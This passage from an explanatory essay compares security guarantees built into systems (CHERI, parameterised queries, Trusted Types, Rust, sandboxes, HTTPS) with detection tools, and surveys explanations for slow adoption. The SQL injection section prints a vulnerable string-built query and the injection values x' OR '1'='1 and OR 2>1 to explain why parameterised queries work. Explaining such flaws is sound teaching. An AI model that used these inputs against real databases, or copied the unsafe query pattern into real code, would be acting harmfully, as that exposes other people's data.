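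By September 2026, SCI had more than £2 million in orders (Tech.eu, *SCI Semiconductor raises £5M to ramp up production of memory-safe chips*, 2026) and £7.7 million in government contracts (Today's Startup News, *SCI Semiconductor Raises £5M as Its Memory-Safe Chip Goes From Concept to*, 2026), so public money was still worth more to it than commercial orders. By comparison, worldwide semiconductor sales in 2022 were $534 billion, according to DSIT's study. In November, Hackett's trade magazine article *SCI Semiconductor* (2026) still described the company as "developing" the chips, so customers could order ICENI, but it was hardly an established product.

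Developers can also buy Sonata, a board for prototyping CHERIoT systems, from an electronics distributor, according to CHERIoT. Sonata imitates the processor on a reprogrammable chip. The European company Codasip licenses a CHERI processor design to chip makers, which must then build it into their own chips. There is still no CHERI phone, laptop or server on general sale.

*CHERI Adoption Global Ecosystem Assessment Q1 2026* (CHERI Alliance, 2026) similarly reports that adoption remains concentrated in evaluation, prototypes and early pilots. This admission is more credible because the Alliance promotes CHERI. The assessment found that software is maturing quickly and hardware more slowly, and it lists the main barriers as limited production silicon, fragmented tools, a shortage of skills, gaps in certification, incomplete standards and limited commercial demand. *CHERI Adoption Programme*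 (Finney, 2026), an interim report on the same government-funded work, put silicon first among the blockers, including a lack of chips that can run Linux.

### A standard that is nearly finished

A common standard would let one version of a compiler or operating system serve chips from many companies. RISC-V International's *CHERI Ratification Plan* scheduled the specification to be frozen in June 2025 and approved by the technical committee in August. That autumn, reviewers were still working out how to name and organise its parts, according to the *RISC-V Tech Journal*. In March 2026 Moore judged the basic mechanisms ready for standardisation, but in May the specification was still a draft. It was marked "Stable", which means that any further changes should be limited.

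Compiler support depends on this process. *[RFC] Upstream target support for CHERI-enabled architectures* proposes adding CHERI to LLVM, a mainstream set of compiler tools, but leaves out Morello, the most capable CHERI system, because it is a prototype and few exist. CHERI's developers maintain Morello support in a separate version of LLVM, so a company interested in Morello has to depend on a small specialist group for its compiler.

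### Who goes first?

Adopting CHERI involves at least three groups: chip companies, software companies and buyers. They might all be better off if they moved together, but each gains little by going first and so has good reason to wait. A chip company that adds CHERI to a new processor pays for the design and the extra chip space straight away, but its customers gain little until developers recompile their software. A software company that goes first pays its engineers to support a processor that its customers do not own. Buyers cannot easily compare the security of two devices, so they have little reason to pay more for the safer one.

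Faily describes a similar deadlock over evidence. Software companies want to know what porting will cost before they commit, chip companies want to know how many customers there will be, and each needs the other to find out.

The British program tried to break the deadlock by paying for hardware so that developers could start on the software. This partly worked. Faily reports that CheriBSD, a version of FreeBSD for CHERI, has several thousand ported packages and a full graphical desktop, but chip makers did not go on to produce processors that could run it in ordinary products. The lack of software was therefore only part of the problem, and the lack of paying customers may be harder to fix with research grants.

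Memory tagging avoids much of this. Pointers stay at 64 bits because the color fits into their unused bits, so most programs can run without being rebuilt. Operating system developers can protect a program's dynamically allocated memory by changing the allocator, and can turn on protection one program at a time. According to DSIT's study, CHERI costs more to adopt than MTE. Tagging uses about 3% more memory, or four bits for every 16 bytes, while CHERI doubles the size of every pointer.

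Apple also had fewer people to persuade because it designs the processor, the compiler tools and the operating system, and sells the finished phone. It could make all the changes itself and recover the cost from sales. Google offered MTE on its Pixel 8 phone in 2023 as a setting for developers and later included it in an optional mode for people at high risk of attack. But Android runs on phones from many manufacturers with different processors, and Google cannot enable MTE on phones that lack the hardware for it. Tagging is therefore opt-in on some Android phones but on by default on new iPhones. CHERI is only starting to become available as a product.

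CHERI's main hardware rival is therefore memory tagging, a mitigation that works partly by chance, rather than a conventional detector such as a virus scanner. Apple's choice of tagging was reasonable. Tagging offered a large improvement to existing phones within a few years, whereas CHERI would have required wider pointers throughout Apple's software and probably changes to many third-party apps.

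### Are safe languages enough?

Some engineers doubt that CHERI is needed. Writing a program in a memory-safe language such as Rust prevents most of the same bugs before it ships, and the program runs on existing chips. Google writes much of Android's new code in such languages. The DSIT study accepts that a safe language makes sense for a new product with no old code.

CHERI's supporters reply that most software is not new. CHERIoT's *CHERI Myths* estimates that open-source projects alone contain around ten billion lines of C and C++, which would cost hundreds of billions to trillions of dollars to rewrite. One remaining memory bug can be enough for an attacker, so a program that is 99% Rust may still be vulnerable. Some code, such as the memory allocator, also has to work below the level at which a language can guarantee safety.

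Safe languages have gaps. Rudra, an analysis tool, found 264 memory-safety bugs in Rust packages, and another project exploited a flaw in the Rust compiler to create such bugs without the `unsafe` keyword. CHERI can contain a malicious library that exploits such a flaw, because the processor checks every memory access, even in code the compiler accepted as safe. The part of CHERI that must be trusted is also much smaller than a compiler. CHERIoT, for example, isolates components using hardware and only about 300 instructions of software.

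CHERIoT's article concedes that CHERI's guarantee is much weaker than Rust's in one respect. A Rust compiler rejects many kinds of memory error at build time, so the developer has to fix them before release. CHERI lets a program ship with such errors and stops it when one occurs, which protects the data but may leave the customer with a crashed device. The article recommends using both.

This reply is more convincing about security than about whether people will buy the chips. CHERI helps most where companies have a lot of old C code, but those companies also have the most software to check and the most equipment to replace. It is easiest to adopt in new embedded products with no old code, but their developers could use Rust on an ordinary chip instead. The estimated cost of rewriting old software is also based on people doing the work, and AI systems may reduce it considerably. The strongest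 market for CHERI is probably equipment that stays in service for decades and contains C code its owners cannot easily replace, such as telephone networks, industrial controls and weapons. Those buyers are also slow to change their hardware.

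## Where did guarantees by construction win?

Some guarantees by construction now protect billions of people. Five cases are documented well enough to compare with the failures: database queries, scripts in web pages, memory-safe languages, application sandboxes and encrypted web traffic. Detectors remained in use alongside all five.

### SQL injection

A website that looks up a customer's orders might build its database query by joining pieces of text:

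```
"SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = '" + name + "'"
```

If a visitor enters `x' OR '1'='1` as the name, the quotation mark after `x` ends the name early, and the database reads the rest as part of the command. The condition is then true for every row, so the visitor gets everybody's orders.

A parameterised query sends the command and the name separately:

```
db.execute("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = ?", [name])
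```

The database works out the structure of the command before it receives the name, so the name can only fill the gap marked by the question mark. If an attacker enters `x' OR '1'='1`, the database looks for a customer with that name and finds nobody. This works for any name an attacker could enter. But a placeholder like the question mark can only stand for a value, not a column name, so developers sometimes still join text into the command when, for example, a visitor chooses which column to sort by.

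The rival detector is the web application firewall, which sits in front of a website and blocks requests that resemble known attacks. A rule that looks for `OR '1'='1` misses `OR 2>1`, which has the same effect, and a broader rule may block someone posting a question about SQL to a programming forum. Wang, Bangert and Kern (2021) object in *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile* that such firewalls only block known categories of attack. But a company can put one in front of an old application that nobody knows how to change, and can block attacks on a newly published flaw within hours.

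Developers fix SQL injection by construction rather than by detection, and Narisetty and colleagues sum up its history as "detection lost and structure won". But companies still buy firewalls to detect attacks. Since 2025 the payment card industry's security standard has required public websites that handle card data to run an automated tool that detects and blocks attacks, and a firewall is the usual choice.

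SQL injection is also still common. MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025) ranks it second, up from third the year before. According to MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Key Insights* (2025), the number of published SQL injection vulnerabilities rose by almost 1,000, partly because there were more reports overall and MITRE changed how it counts them. The Hacker News reported that attackers were exploiting a SQL injection flaw in Drupal, a widely used system for running websites, in May 2026. SANS, a security training company, lists another from the same year in WordPress. Both projects have long given their developers a safe way to build queries.

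Most programming languages have supported parameterised queries for decades, and popular web frameworks use them for routine lookups. But developers can usually still build queries by joining strings, which is unsafe and just as easy to type. The guarantee therefore covers only the queries that use parameters, not the whole application.

Google closed this gap in its own code. In 2013 it began changing the functions that its programmers use to query its main databases, according to *An Overview of Google's Commitment to Secure by Design* (2024). Instead of ordinary text, the functions now accept only a special type, `TrustedSqlString`, which a programmer can build from text written in the program itself or from other trusted sources, but not from a visitor's input. If a programmer passes in unsafe text, the program does not compile. Google reports no SQL injection vulnerabilities over the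 following decade in the hundreds of applications that use these databases.

### Cross-site scripting

Cross-site scripting is a similar flaw in web pages. If a site displays visitors' comments without changing them, an attacker can post a comment that contains a script, and the script runs in the browser of everyone who views the comment. The script can read or change anything on the site that those readers can.

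The basic fix is escaping, which replaces special characters with codes that the browser displays as text instead of treating as markup. For example, `<` becomes `&lt;`. Programmers used to do this by hand, and a large application may have hundreds of places where a single omission would let an attacker run code. Automatic escaping does it by default. The better systems also adjust for where the text will appear, because a link that begins with `javascript:` can run code without containing any character that needs escaping.

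Google again used special types. Browsers have about 60 functions and properties that may run text as code. Google's compilers check a list of those known to be dangerous and reject any program that passes them ordinary text instead of a value produced by a safe library. A programmer with a good reason can ask security staff for an exemption. Wang and colleagues counted fewer than eight such requests a week in the first months of large-scale use, while programmers were making about 10,000 changes a week to JavaScript code.

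The compiler can miss things, partly because JavaScript lets programs disguise the type of a value. Google therefore proposed Trusted Types, which makes the browser itself reject ordinary text in dangerous places. According to *Trusted Types* (Kotowicz, 2021), this would have stopped at least 61% of the flaws of this kind that Google's code analysis had missed. By mid-2021 Google had moved 130 services to Trusted Types and had found no such flaws in them since.

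The reported bug counts are striking:

- One product had 10 cross-site scripting flaws in its browser code in the year before it adopted the compiler checks, 2 during the year of adoption and 1 in the year after.
- In the early 2010s, a large application such as Gmail typically had tens of cross-site scripting flaws a year, as Kern (2024), in *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety*, recalls.
- By 2024, Google was receiving fewer than one report a year in total for hundreds of applications built on its safe frameworks.

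These are Google's own figures, and they depend on how hard people look for bugs. But Google pays outsiders to report bugs, so it probably hasn't missed many easy to find. The first product was only one case, and its team was unusually committed. Across the company, Wang and colleagues found that a growing proportion of the remaining flaws came from old code the checks did not cover, which suggests that the checks were keeping flaws out of new code.

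Browser makers had meanwhile tried detection. Internet Explorer 8, and later Chrome, included filters that looked for scripts appearing in both a request and the returned page. Attackers found ways around the filters and could sometimes use them to disable a site's legitimate scripts. Microsoft removed its filter from Edge in 2018, and Google removed Chrome's in 2019.

Outside Google, Trusted Types has spread more slowly. Microsoft's code editor Visual Studio Code adopted it in January 2021. An automatic tool found 108 violations in the editor's nearly one million lines, and three quarters were trivial to fix. Facebook's main application had a long tail of violations. A site also has to turn Trusted Types on, and not every browser supported it until Firefox did in early 2026, according to URIports' *Beyond script-src*. The security researcher Michał Bentkowski warned in PortSwigger's coverage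 that a site's own rules for producing trusted values may contain mistakes.

Cross-site scripting still comes first in MITRE's ranking. *CISA review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes* (Zorz, 2026) reports that CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, blames organisational culture for the survival of such well-understood flaws. Culture probably matters, but Google also had practical advantages. Its programmers share one code repository and one set of compilers, and somebody has to review every change. Wang and colleagues list these among the conditions that made adoption easy. A small company that runs its website on 40 outside plug-ins has none of these advantages.

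### Rust in Android

Rust prevents most memory bugs by having the compiler track which part of a program owns each piece of data. When the owner finishes with the data, the program releases the memory, and the compiler rejects any code that could use it afterwards. Java also prevents such bugs, but it uses a background process to find unused memory, which makes it a poor fit for the lowest layers of an operating system, which used to require C or C++.

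Google began using Rust in Android's own code around 2021, without trying to rewrite the existing C and C++. By Android 13, released in 2022, about 21% of new C, C++ and Rust code was in Rust, according to Google (2022). In the first three quarters of 2025, Google's Android developers added slightly more lines of Rust than of C++, after subtracting the lines they removed.

Memory-safety bugs fell from 76% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019 to 24% in 2024, and *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) reports that they fell below 20% in 2025. The number of these bugs also fell, from 223 in 2019 to fewer than 50 in 2024 (The Hacker News, 2025), so the drop in share wasn't merely due to an increase in other bugs.

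The total fell quickly even though most of the old code remained, because developers keep finding and fixing bugs in old code, so a bug is more likely to be in recent code. *Memory Safety at Scale* (Rebert, 2026) describes vulnerabilities as having a half-life. If the half-life is *h* years, a fraction 2^(−*t*/*h*) of the original bugs remains after *t* years. With a half-life of three years, for example, nine-year-old code has only an eighth of its original bugs. When developers switch to Rust for new code, they stop adding memory bugs while the old ones gradually disappear.

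Vander Stoep estimates that Android's Rust code has 0.2 memory-safety vulnerabilities per million lines, compared with about 1,000 for its C and C++. The ratio is uncertain because the Rust figure comes from a single bug in about five million lines, and researchers have had many more years to search the C and C++. But the estimate would have to be wrong by a very large factor to change the conclusion that the Rust code has fewer of these vulnerabilities per line.

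That one bug was a buffer overflow in an image-reading library, which Google fixed before release. It was in code marked `unsafe`, where a programmer can do things the compiler cannot check. About 4% of Android's Rust code is marked this way. Android's memory allocator would have made the bug unexploitable anyway, because it puts inaccessible memory around large blocks of data. Rust's guarantee also depends on its standard library. Bae (2026), in *FORGE Lab uses agentic tools to identify memory safety issues in Rust*, reports memory bugs there, including some that a program could trigger without using `unsafe`.

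Rust also made Android's developers more productive. Rust changes spent about 25% less time in review than C++ changes, and developers had to undo medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often. Developers may choose Rust for tasks that suit it, which a controlled experiment would rule out, but Vander Stoep compared changes of similar size, and many of the same people wrote in both languages. Unlike Jif's users, Android's developers seem to have saved time once they had learned the language.

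Android still has many flaws. Google fixed 216 in November 2026, including one that let attackers run code without any action by the user, according to The Hacker News' *Google Issues Patches for Critical Android Flaw That Could Allow RCE* (2026). Other software is much further from memory safety. Rebert tentatively suggests that the wider move to it could last until 2060, or 2035 if AI systems translate old code.

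### Sandboxes in browsers and phones

When Google launched Chrome in 2008, it put the code that interprets web pages into separate, sandboxed processes that could not open the user's files. That code is large and handles input from strangers, so attackers often find bugs in it. An attacker who takes over one of these processes usually needs a second bug to escape the sandbox. When a page requests a photo, the trusted part of the browser shows the user a file picker and passes the page only the file the user chooses. This is very close to handing over a capability, and the user doesn't need to know what a capability is.

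In 2018 Chrome began giving each website its own process on desktop, mainly because of the speculative execution attacks published that year. Google turned this on for 99% of desktop users, even though it increased Chrome's memory use by roughly 10 to 13%. Most web developers did not have to change anything. Users received the protection through an automatic update, and few would have known there was a setting for it.

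Android has sandboxed apps since its first release in 2008 by giving each one a separate Linux user account. An app still has ambient authority, but mostly over its own files. Since 2014, Android has also used SELinux, which grew out of Smalley's Flask project, to enforce mandatory rules on every process. Google said in 2021 that more than three billion devices were running Android, so some of the ideas behind the Orange Book have reached far more people through phones than through evaluated computers.

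When Apple opened the iPhone's App Store in 2008, it required every outside app to run in a sandbox. Developers had no existing iPhone apps to adapt and no other official way to reach ordinary customers. Sandboxing was harder to impose on the Mac, where developers already had large programs and could sell them elsewhere. In 2012 Apple required it for apps in the Mac App Store but not for other Mac software. Some developers left the store. The text editor BBEdit withdrew in 2014 and returned in 2019, after Apple had made the sandbox more flexible.

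A sandbox cannot protect people from an app that asks for access and gets it, or from a fake banking app that asks for a password. Android therefore also uses Google Play Protect to detect harmful apps. Android (2026) notes in a security bulletin that Play Protect is on by default on devices with Google's services and matters most for people who install apps from outside Google Play.

### Encrypted web traffic

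Anyone who controls the network between a browser and a website can read and change plain HTTP traffic. In 2010 a free browser extension called Firesheep let people on open Wi-Fi take over strangers' Facebook accounts with a couple of clicks. HTTPS prevents this by encrypting the traffic and checking that nobody has altered it. The site also presents a certificate, in which an outside authority confirms that the site's encryption key belongs to its domain name. The guarantee depends on the strength of the cryptography and the honesty of every authority the browser trusts.

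Netscape introduced the encryption behind HTTPS in the mid-1990s, but in late 2015 only about 40% of the pages that Firefox loaded used it. Banks and shops had reason to pay for a certificate, install it by hand and remember to renew it, but the owner of a small blog usually did not.

Let's Encrypt, a non-profit authority backed by Mozilla and others, opened to the public in December 2015. It gives certificates away, and software handles the whole process:

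1. A program on the web server asks for a certificate for the site's domain name.
2. Let's Encrypt replies with a random code.
3. The program publishes a file based on the code at a particular address on the site.
4. Let's Encrypt fetches the file, which shows that whoever made the request controls the site.
5. The program receives the certificate, installs it and repeats the process before it expires.

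Let's Encrypt originally made every certificate valid for 90 days, partly to encourage owners to automate renewal. Hosting companies could then turn on HTTPS for all their customers at once. WordPress.com did so in 2016 for the sites it hosted on custom domains, and the site owners did not have to do anything.

Browser makers put pressure on the sites that still used HTTP. From January 2017 Chrome displayed "Not secure" beside HTTP pages that asked for passwords or card numbers, and from July 2018 beside all HTTP pages. Browser makers also limited some new features, such as access to a visitor's location, to encrypted sites. A warning on every HTTP page would have been much harder to defend when certificates still cost money.

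HTTPS reached 58% of Firefox page loads in June 2017 and 81% in early 2020. In 2025 Google put the share in Chrome at 95% to 99%. Nobody can say how much of this growth was due to Let's Encrypt, since Google had also started favoring encrypted sites in its search results in 2014, and the largest sites, which account for a lot of traffic, could easily afford certificates. But free, automatic certificates are probably why millions of small sites adopted HTTPS.

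HTTPS does not verify that a site is honest, so criminals use it for fake login pages too. Browsers still rely on lists and statistical models to warn people about these pages. False certificates also have to be detected. In 2011 an intruder obtained some for Google and other sites from the Dutch certificate authority DigiNotar. Chrome now requires authorities to record certificates in public logs, where domain owners can spot any they did not request.

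### What the five cases share

| Case | Who could change the default | Work for an ordinary developer | What people could count | Detection still in use |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | Framework developers, and Google for its own code | Little for routine queries | Injection flaws | Web application firewalls |
| Cross-site scripting | Google, for its own frameworks | Little in new code, more in old code | Reports from outside researchers | Firewalls and code scanners |
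| Rust in Android | Google | Learning a language, then less rework | Memory-safety vulnerabilities | Tools that search for bugs |
| Sandboxes | Browser makers, Apple and Google | None for most web pages, some for apps | Users protected | Malware and phishing warnings |
| HTTPS | Browser makers and hosting companies | Little or none after automation | Share of pages loaded | Phishing warnings and certificate logs |

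Four features recur among the successes. In most cases, a platform owner could change the default for many people at once, as Meta could with Policy Zones and Apple with memory tagging. The owners often started with new code or a new platform and left old software for later. Developers had little extra work, or soon got the time back. People could count the benefit, which gave the engineers a way to justify the next stage.

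Not every case has all four. HTTPS and browser sandboxes covered old websites as well as new ones because the protection worked outside the pages, which could mostly stay the same. Outside companies such as Google, no single owner controls the platforms where SQL injection occurs, which may be one reason it is still so common.

The sample is also biased. Successful projects publish their numbers, and Google supplied most of the figures here. A company that tried Trusted Types and gave up after a month is unlikely to write a paper about it. Some of the failures had the same features as the successes. Java's Security Manager, for instance, had a platform owner who could have made it the default.

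## Which explanations fit both the failures and the successes?

Economists, sociologists and engineers have offered at least seven explanations for the slow spread of strong security. Most seem to explain the failures, but a useful explanation must also fit HTTPS, browser sandboxes and Rust in Android, which spread despite some of the same obstacles. To explain why guarantees lose to detection, it must also identify an obstacle that hinders guarantees more than detectors.

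### Buyers who cannot judge security

Ross Anderson's *Why Information Security is Hard* (2001) applied the economist George Akerlof's "market for lemons" to security products. Suppose a used-car market has 100 good cars worth $3,000 each and 100 bad ones worth $1,000 each, and only the sellers know which are which. Buyers will pay the average value, $2,000, so the owners of good cars don't sell. Once buyers notice that only bad cars are on offer, the price falls to $1,000. In the same way, customers who can't tell a sound security product from a weak one won't pay extra for the sound one.

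*The Market for Silver Bullets* objects that the sellers of security don't know how good their products are either. *Ruminations on the State of the Security Nation*, a 2010 blog post that takes the same view, cites a survey in which nearly every company rated its security controls equally effective, although the number and cost of their incidents varied widely. The post concedes that the survey doesn't settle whether sellers know more than buyers.

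The Orange Book is a good test of the lemons theory, because an official grade is the usual remedy for hidden quality. Ross Anderson thought the incentives were better under the Orange Book than under its successor, the Common Criteria. The government evaluated products that it would rely on itself, whereas vendors paid for Common Criteria evaluations and could look for a lenient evaluator. But even with the Orange Book's grades, most customers bought the weaker systems. Google, on the other hand, adopted Rust in Android even though phone buyers cannot see how much of the code is written in it.

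Customers also struggle to judge the quality of detectors. Few can tell whether a virus scanner misses 2% or 20% of new attacks. The lemons theory may therefore explain why the market undersupplies good security of every kind, but it doesn't explain a preference for detection.

### Who pays and who gains

A related explanation is that the people who could fix a weakness often don't suffer from it. Ross Anderson's example is cash machine fraud. A US bank that rejected a customer's complaint had to prove the customer wrong, while customers in Britain, Norway and the Netherlands had to prove the bank wrong, which was almost impossible. US banks had much less fraud even though they spent less on security, because they had a reason to spend the money well.

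*Information Security Economics* compares connecting an insecure computer to the internet with burning a coal fire, since other people bear part of the cost of each. Watson and colleagues see a potential market failure in memory safety for a similar reason. A vendor that does without it saves money immediately, while the losses come later and fall on many people.

This explanation also fits several of the successes. Meta paid for Policy Zones and reduced its own legal risk, and Google paid for the move to Rust and got back some of its engineers' time. It fits Digital's VAX security kernel less well, because an agency that paid for the system would also have received the protection.

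Detection has a version of the same problem. The economist Hal Varian observed that people might happily spend $100 on antivirus software to protect themselves, but hardly $1 to stop others from using their computers to attack Amazon or Microsoft. However, the buyer of a detector can act alone, as when a hospital buys a malware scanner. To run its records program in a Capsicum sandbox, the hospital has to persuade the program's developer to do the work, and the developer may gain very little.

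### The adoption threshold

CHERI and other defenses are held back partly because the first adopters gain little. *Bootstrapping the Adoption of Internet Security Protocols* (Ozment and Schechter, 2006) models this problem. Let *x* be the share of users who have adopted a technology, *B*(*x*) the benefit to each adopter and *c* the cost of adopting. Users adopt only when *B*(*x*) > *c*.

Suppose adoption costs each of 9,000 users $100 and brings each a benefit of $300 if all of them adopt. If the benefit is proportional to the fraction *x* of users who have adopted, then *B*(*x*) = 300*x*, which exceeds the cost only when *x* is above one third, or 3,000 users. Anyone who adopts before then loses money at first, so nobody starts, even though everyone would be $200 better off if they all adopted together.

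Ozment and Schechter mainly use a different formula, in which each new member adds less value than the one before. If *M* is the benefit at full adoption, then *B*(*x*) = ln(1 + *Qx*), where *Q* = *e*^*M* − 1. The same amounts, in hundreds of dollars, give *M* = 3, *c* = 1 and a threshold of only 9%. Doubling the cost raises the threshold to about 33%, so a modest change in cost can decide whether adoption gets going.

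Protocols that prove who sent a message also need many senders to adopt them before they are useful. Until then, a recipient who accepts unsigned email can be fooled by a forger who leaves out the signature, and one who rejects it loses contact with everyone who hasn't started signing. A virus scanner protects its first customer even if nobody else buys one.

The threshold may apply to internet routing as well as to CHERI. *Modeling Adoptability of Secure BGP Protocols* (Chan, Dash and colleagues, 2006) simulated internet providers' decisions because several secure routing protocols had made little progress towards adoption. But the threshold does not explain Capsicum, which protects a program even if no other program uses it.

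SSH, a program for logging in to a distant computer over an encrypted connection, provides a more precise test. It replaced telnet, which sent passwords in readable form. According to *How and Why More Secure Technologies Succeed in Legacy Markets* (Rosasco and Larochelle, 2003), SSH came out in July 1995 and had around 20,000 users by the end of that year and an estimated two million by the end of 2000. Although SSH needs software at both ends of the connection, its adoption threshold was low because most people logged in to only a few computers, and an organisation could get nearly all the benefit by switching its own machines.

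Secure file transfer spread much more slowly, although it often used the same encryption and gave the same protection against password theft. Rosasco and Larochelle explain the difference mainly by what each program offered its users. SSH closely imitated some of the commands it replaced and could automatically show a remote program's windows on the user's own screen, which had previously required manual setup. The file-transfer programs offered no comparable convenience, lacked some features of the older FTP and came in incompatible versions. A stolen FTP password also often harmed only one user, while a stolen login could endanger a whole computer and make work for its administrator.

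### Old software and "worse is better"

SSH's success suggests that compatibility may matter more than the strength of the protection. Richard Gabriel, a designer of the programming language Lisp, made a similar but more general argument around 1990 in *The Rise of Worse is Better*. He expected designers who want "the right thing" and accept no incorrect behavior to lose to people who released something simpler that ran on almost any machine. Users would get used to its faults, and its developers would later improve it until it was almost the right thing. His main examples of the simpler approach were the operating system Unix and the language C, on which much of today's software still depends.

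Ross Anderson adds an economic reason. The owner of a new platform has to attract developers quickly, because customers choose the platform with the most programs. Mandatory security makes developers' work harder and so reduces the platform's value. Releasing an insecure product early and fixing it later can therefore be rational. But by then, developers have written programs that depend on the insecure behavior.

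Compatibility with existing software explains many of the failures and successes. KeyKOS needed new programs to make full use of its protection, and Jif needed annotated libraries, whereas most web pages worked in Chrome's sandbox without changes. Compatibility also explains why Apple could require sandboxing more easily on the iPhone than on the Mac.

Compatibility doesn't explain every case. The VAX security kernel ran customers' existing operating systems, and Ruby's taint checking worked without annotations, yet both failed. Meta's Policy Zones succeeded even though it took a great deal of engineering work. Compatibility reduces the work of adoption, but an organization still needs a reason to do the rest, as Meta had.

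### Writing the rules

Somebody has to write the rules that a guarantee enforces. This was a large part of the trouble with Java's Security Manager, whose users often gave up and granted every permission. It also made work for users of Jif and of the military's labeled systems, which needed constant exceptions.

Most of the successes, including parameterised queries and browser sandboxes, avoided the problem by having one rule for everybody, which the owner of a framework or browser can write once. A rule about which employees may see which documents differs between organisations and has to be updated whenever somebody changes jobs.

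However, CHERI's basic memory protection doesn't require users to write a policy either, and it has hardly spread. Policy Zones needed an enormous amount of policy work. The difficulty of writing rules is therefore a good explanation for why some permission and labeling systems failed, but not for why guarantees fail in general.

### When refusing was reasonable

Buyers may also have understood a guarantee and decided that it wasn't worth the price. Butler Lampson, a computer scientist who worked on early protection systems, argued in 2004 that practical security balances the cost of protection against the risk of loss. If a company has a 1% chance each year of losing $500,000, its expected loss is $5,000 a year. Spending $50,000 a year on a guarantee that removes that risk would usually be a mistake.

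Cormac Herley of Microsoft Research applied similar reasoning to users' time in 2009. He estimated that if people spent even a minute a day checking web addresses for signs of fraud, their time would be worth about a hundred times all the money lost to fake websites. On this view, people who ignore advice to check addresses are often sensible to do so.

The Orange Book is the clearest case of a guarantee against a threat that most buyers, including most companies, didn't face. Lipner describes one buyer that did, the Air Force's Military Airlift Command. Its work was largely unclassified, but it occasionally flew secret missions with the same aircraft and crews, so it wanted people without clearances to share a computer that held classified information.

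The same explanation fits the Security Manager, whose maintainers thought it did little against the most dangerous kinds of flaw. It doesn't fit Ruby's taint checking, because websites did suffer from the attacks it was meant to stop. It doesn't fit CHERI either, because most critical vulnerabilities are memory bugs. Lampson's calculation also leaves out losses that fall on other people, so refusing CHERI may be in a manufacturer's own interest even if its customers would be better off with it.

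### Rewards that nobody sees

The sociologist Everett Rogers, who studied how new ideas spread, attributes the slow spread of preventive ones partly to delayed rewards in *Diffusion of preventive innovations* (2002). People have to act now to avoid something that may never happen. A company that installs a perfect defense may see no successful attacks for a year, but it might have seen none anyway.

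People may not adopt an innovation even when its benefit is visible. *Diffusion of Innovations* (Rogers, 2003) recounts that in 1601 Captain James Lancaster gave lemon juice to the sailors on one of his four ships. Those sailors stayed healthy, while 110 of the 278 men on the other ships had died of scurvy by the middle of the voyage. The British Navy did not adopt citrus juice until 1795, though it readily accepted new ships and guns in the meantime.

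Every guarantee is preventive, so prevention alone cannot explain why some succeeded and others failed. But several of the successes also had a benefit that people noticed immediately. Rust reduced the time spent on reviews, and SSH saved its users some setup. Parameterised queries can handle names like O'Brien, whose apostrophe may break a query built by joining text.

Detectors are preventive too. *The diffusion of innovations perspective* (2010) lists burglar alarms alongside low-salt diets and flood insurance as things it is hard to persuade people to adopt. But people can tell when an alarm has worked, because it makes a noise.

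### What a detector offers instead

A company's security department can buy a detector as a finished product and install it without asking the developers of the company's other software to change anything. A guarantee usually depends on how those developers build their programs, so the department may have nothing to buy. A familiar brand also protects the person who chooses it. Ross Anderson observes that managers often knowingly buy inferior products from well-known suppliers, because this makes them less likely to lose their jobs if something goes wrong.

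Staff can also tune a detector. Suppose an online shop receives a million requests a day, 100 of them hostile. At a strict setting, its firewall blocks 95 of the hostile requests but also 1% of the innocent ones, or about 10,000. At a looser setting, it blocks only 70 hostile requests but 0.01% of innocent ones, or about 100. The shop may well prefer the looser setting. If customers complain, its staff can change the setting and change it back the same day. Few guarantees are so easy to adjust, although the logging mode in Policy Zones comes close.

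Finally, detectors produce alerts, which help a security manager justify next year's budget. The manager can show the board a chart of 4,000 blocked attacks, whereas a guarantee that makes the same attacks harmless may leave nothing to count. The chart is weak evidence of safety, since many of those attacks might have failed anyway and it omits the ones the detector missed.

These advantages match what researchers have found about other innovations. *Exploring Perceptions of Colorectal Cancer and Fecal Immunochemical Testing Among African Americans*, a public health paper, lists five attributes that explain 49% to 87% of the variation in adoption rates:

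- relative advantage over what people already use;
- compatibility, or fit with what people already value;
- complexity, or how hard it seems to use;
- trialability, or whether people can experiment with it first;
- observability, or whether others can see the results.

A guarantee may have the greater relative advantage, but a detector often does better on the other four attributes. A detector is especially easy to try, because a company can start with one office or let it send alerts without blocking anything. The percentages come from research on other kinds of innovation, so they don't show how much each attribute matters in security.

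### Is detection a mistake?

Marcus Ranum, who designed some of the first commercial firewalls, thought the popularity of detection was foolish. In a 2005 essay he called detection "enumerating badness". He wrote that a typical antivirus program checked for about 75,000 viruses, while he had only about 30 legitimate programs on his computer, so it would be much easier to list those 30 and refuse to run anything else.

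Ranum's comparison is a strong argument for allowing only approved programs over blocking known bad ones, but he chose an easy case because he knew what he needed to run. A large company has thousands of employees who need different programs, and someone has to approve every new program and every update. A list of approved programs also doesn't stop an attacker from taking over a program on the list, such as the journalist's PDF reader.

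Another reply is that partial protection now may be better than full protection later. *The Rise of Worse is Better* recommends releasing half of the right thing first and improving it once people depend on it. *Better Than Nothing Security*, a blog post about encrypting internet traffic without first verifying who is at the other end, criticises people who are "willing to be insecure" until they get the best security.

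Suppose a company faces 100 attacks a year. A detector installed today that stops 60% of them will stop 600 over ten years. A guarantee that takes five years to build and then stops every attack will stop only 500 in the same period. But if attackers learn to avoid the detector and its success rate falls by five percentage points each year, it will stop only 375. The comparison also assumes that every attack does the same damage. If one successful attack is enough to steal everything, a detector that stops 60 out of 100 is of little use.

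The company would do best to install the detector now and keep working on the guarantee. The detector would stop 800 attacks if its success rate held steady. But it could also make the problem seem less urgent and lead the company to cancel work on the guarantee.

### Comparing the explanations

Each explanation in the table names an obstacle. ✓ means the explanation predicts the right outcome, because the obstacle was present in a failure or absent in a success. ✗ means it predicts the wrong outcome, and – means the evidence is mixed or unclear. "Non-event" means adopters saw no reward except fewer attacks. The table omits Caja because another guarantee replaced it.

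| Case | Spread widely? | Hidden quality | Split costs | Threshold | Non-event | Old software | Policy work | Wrong threat |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| KeyKOS | No | – | – | ✓ | – | ✓ | – | – |
| Capsicum | No | – | ✓ | ✗ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✗ |
| Java's Security Manager | No | – | – | ✓ | ✓ | – | ✓ | ✓ |
| VAX security kernel | No | ✗ | ✗ | ✗ | ✗ | ✗ | – | ✓ |
| Jif | No | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | – |
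| Ruby's taint checking | No | – | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✗ | ✗ | ✗ |
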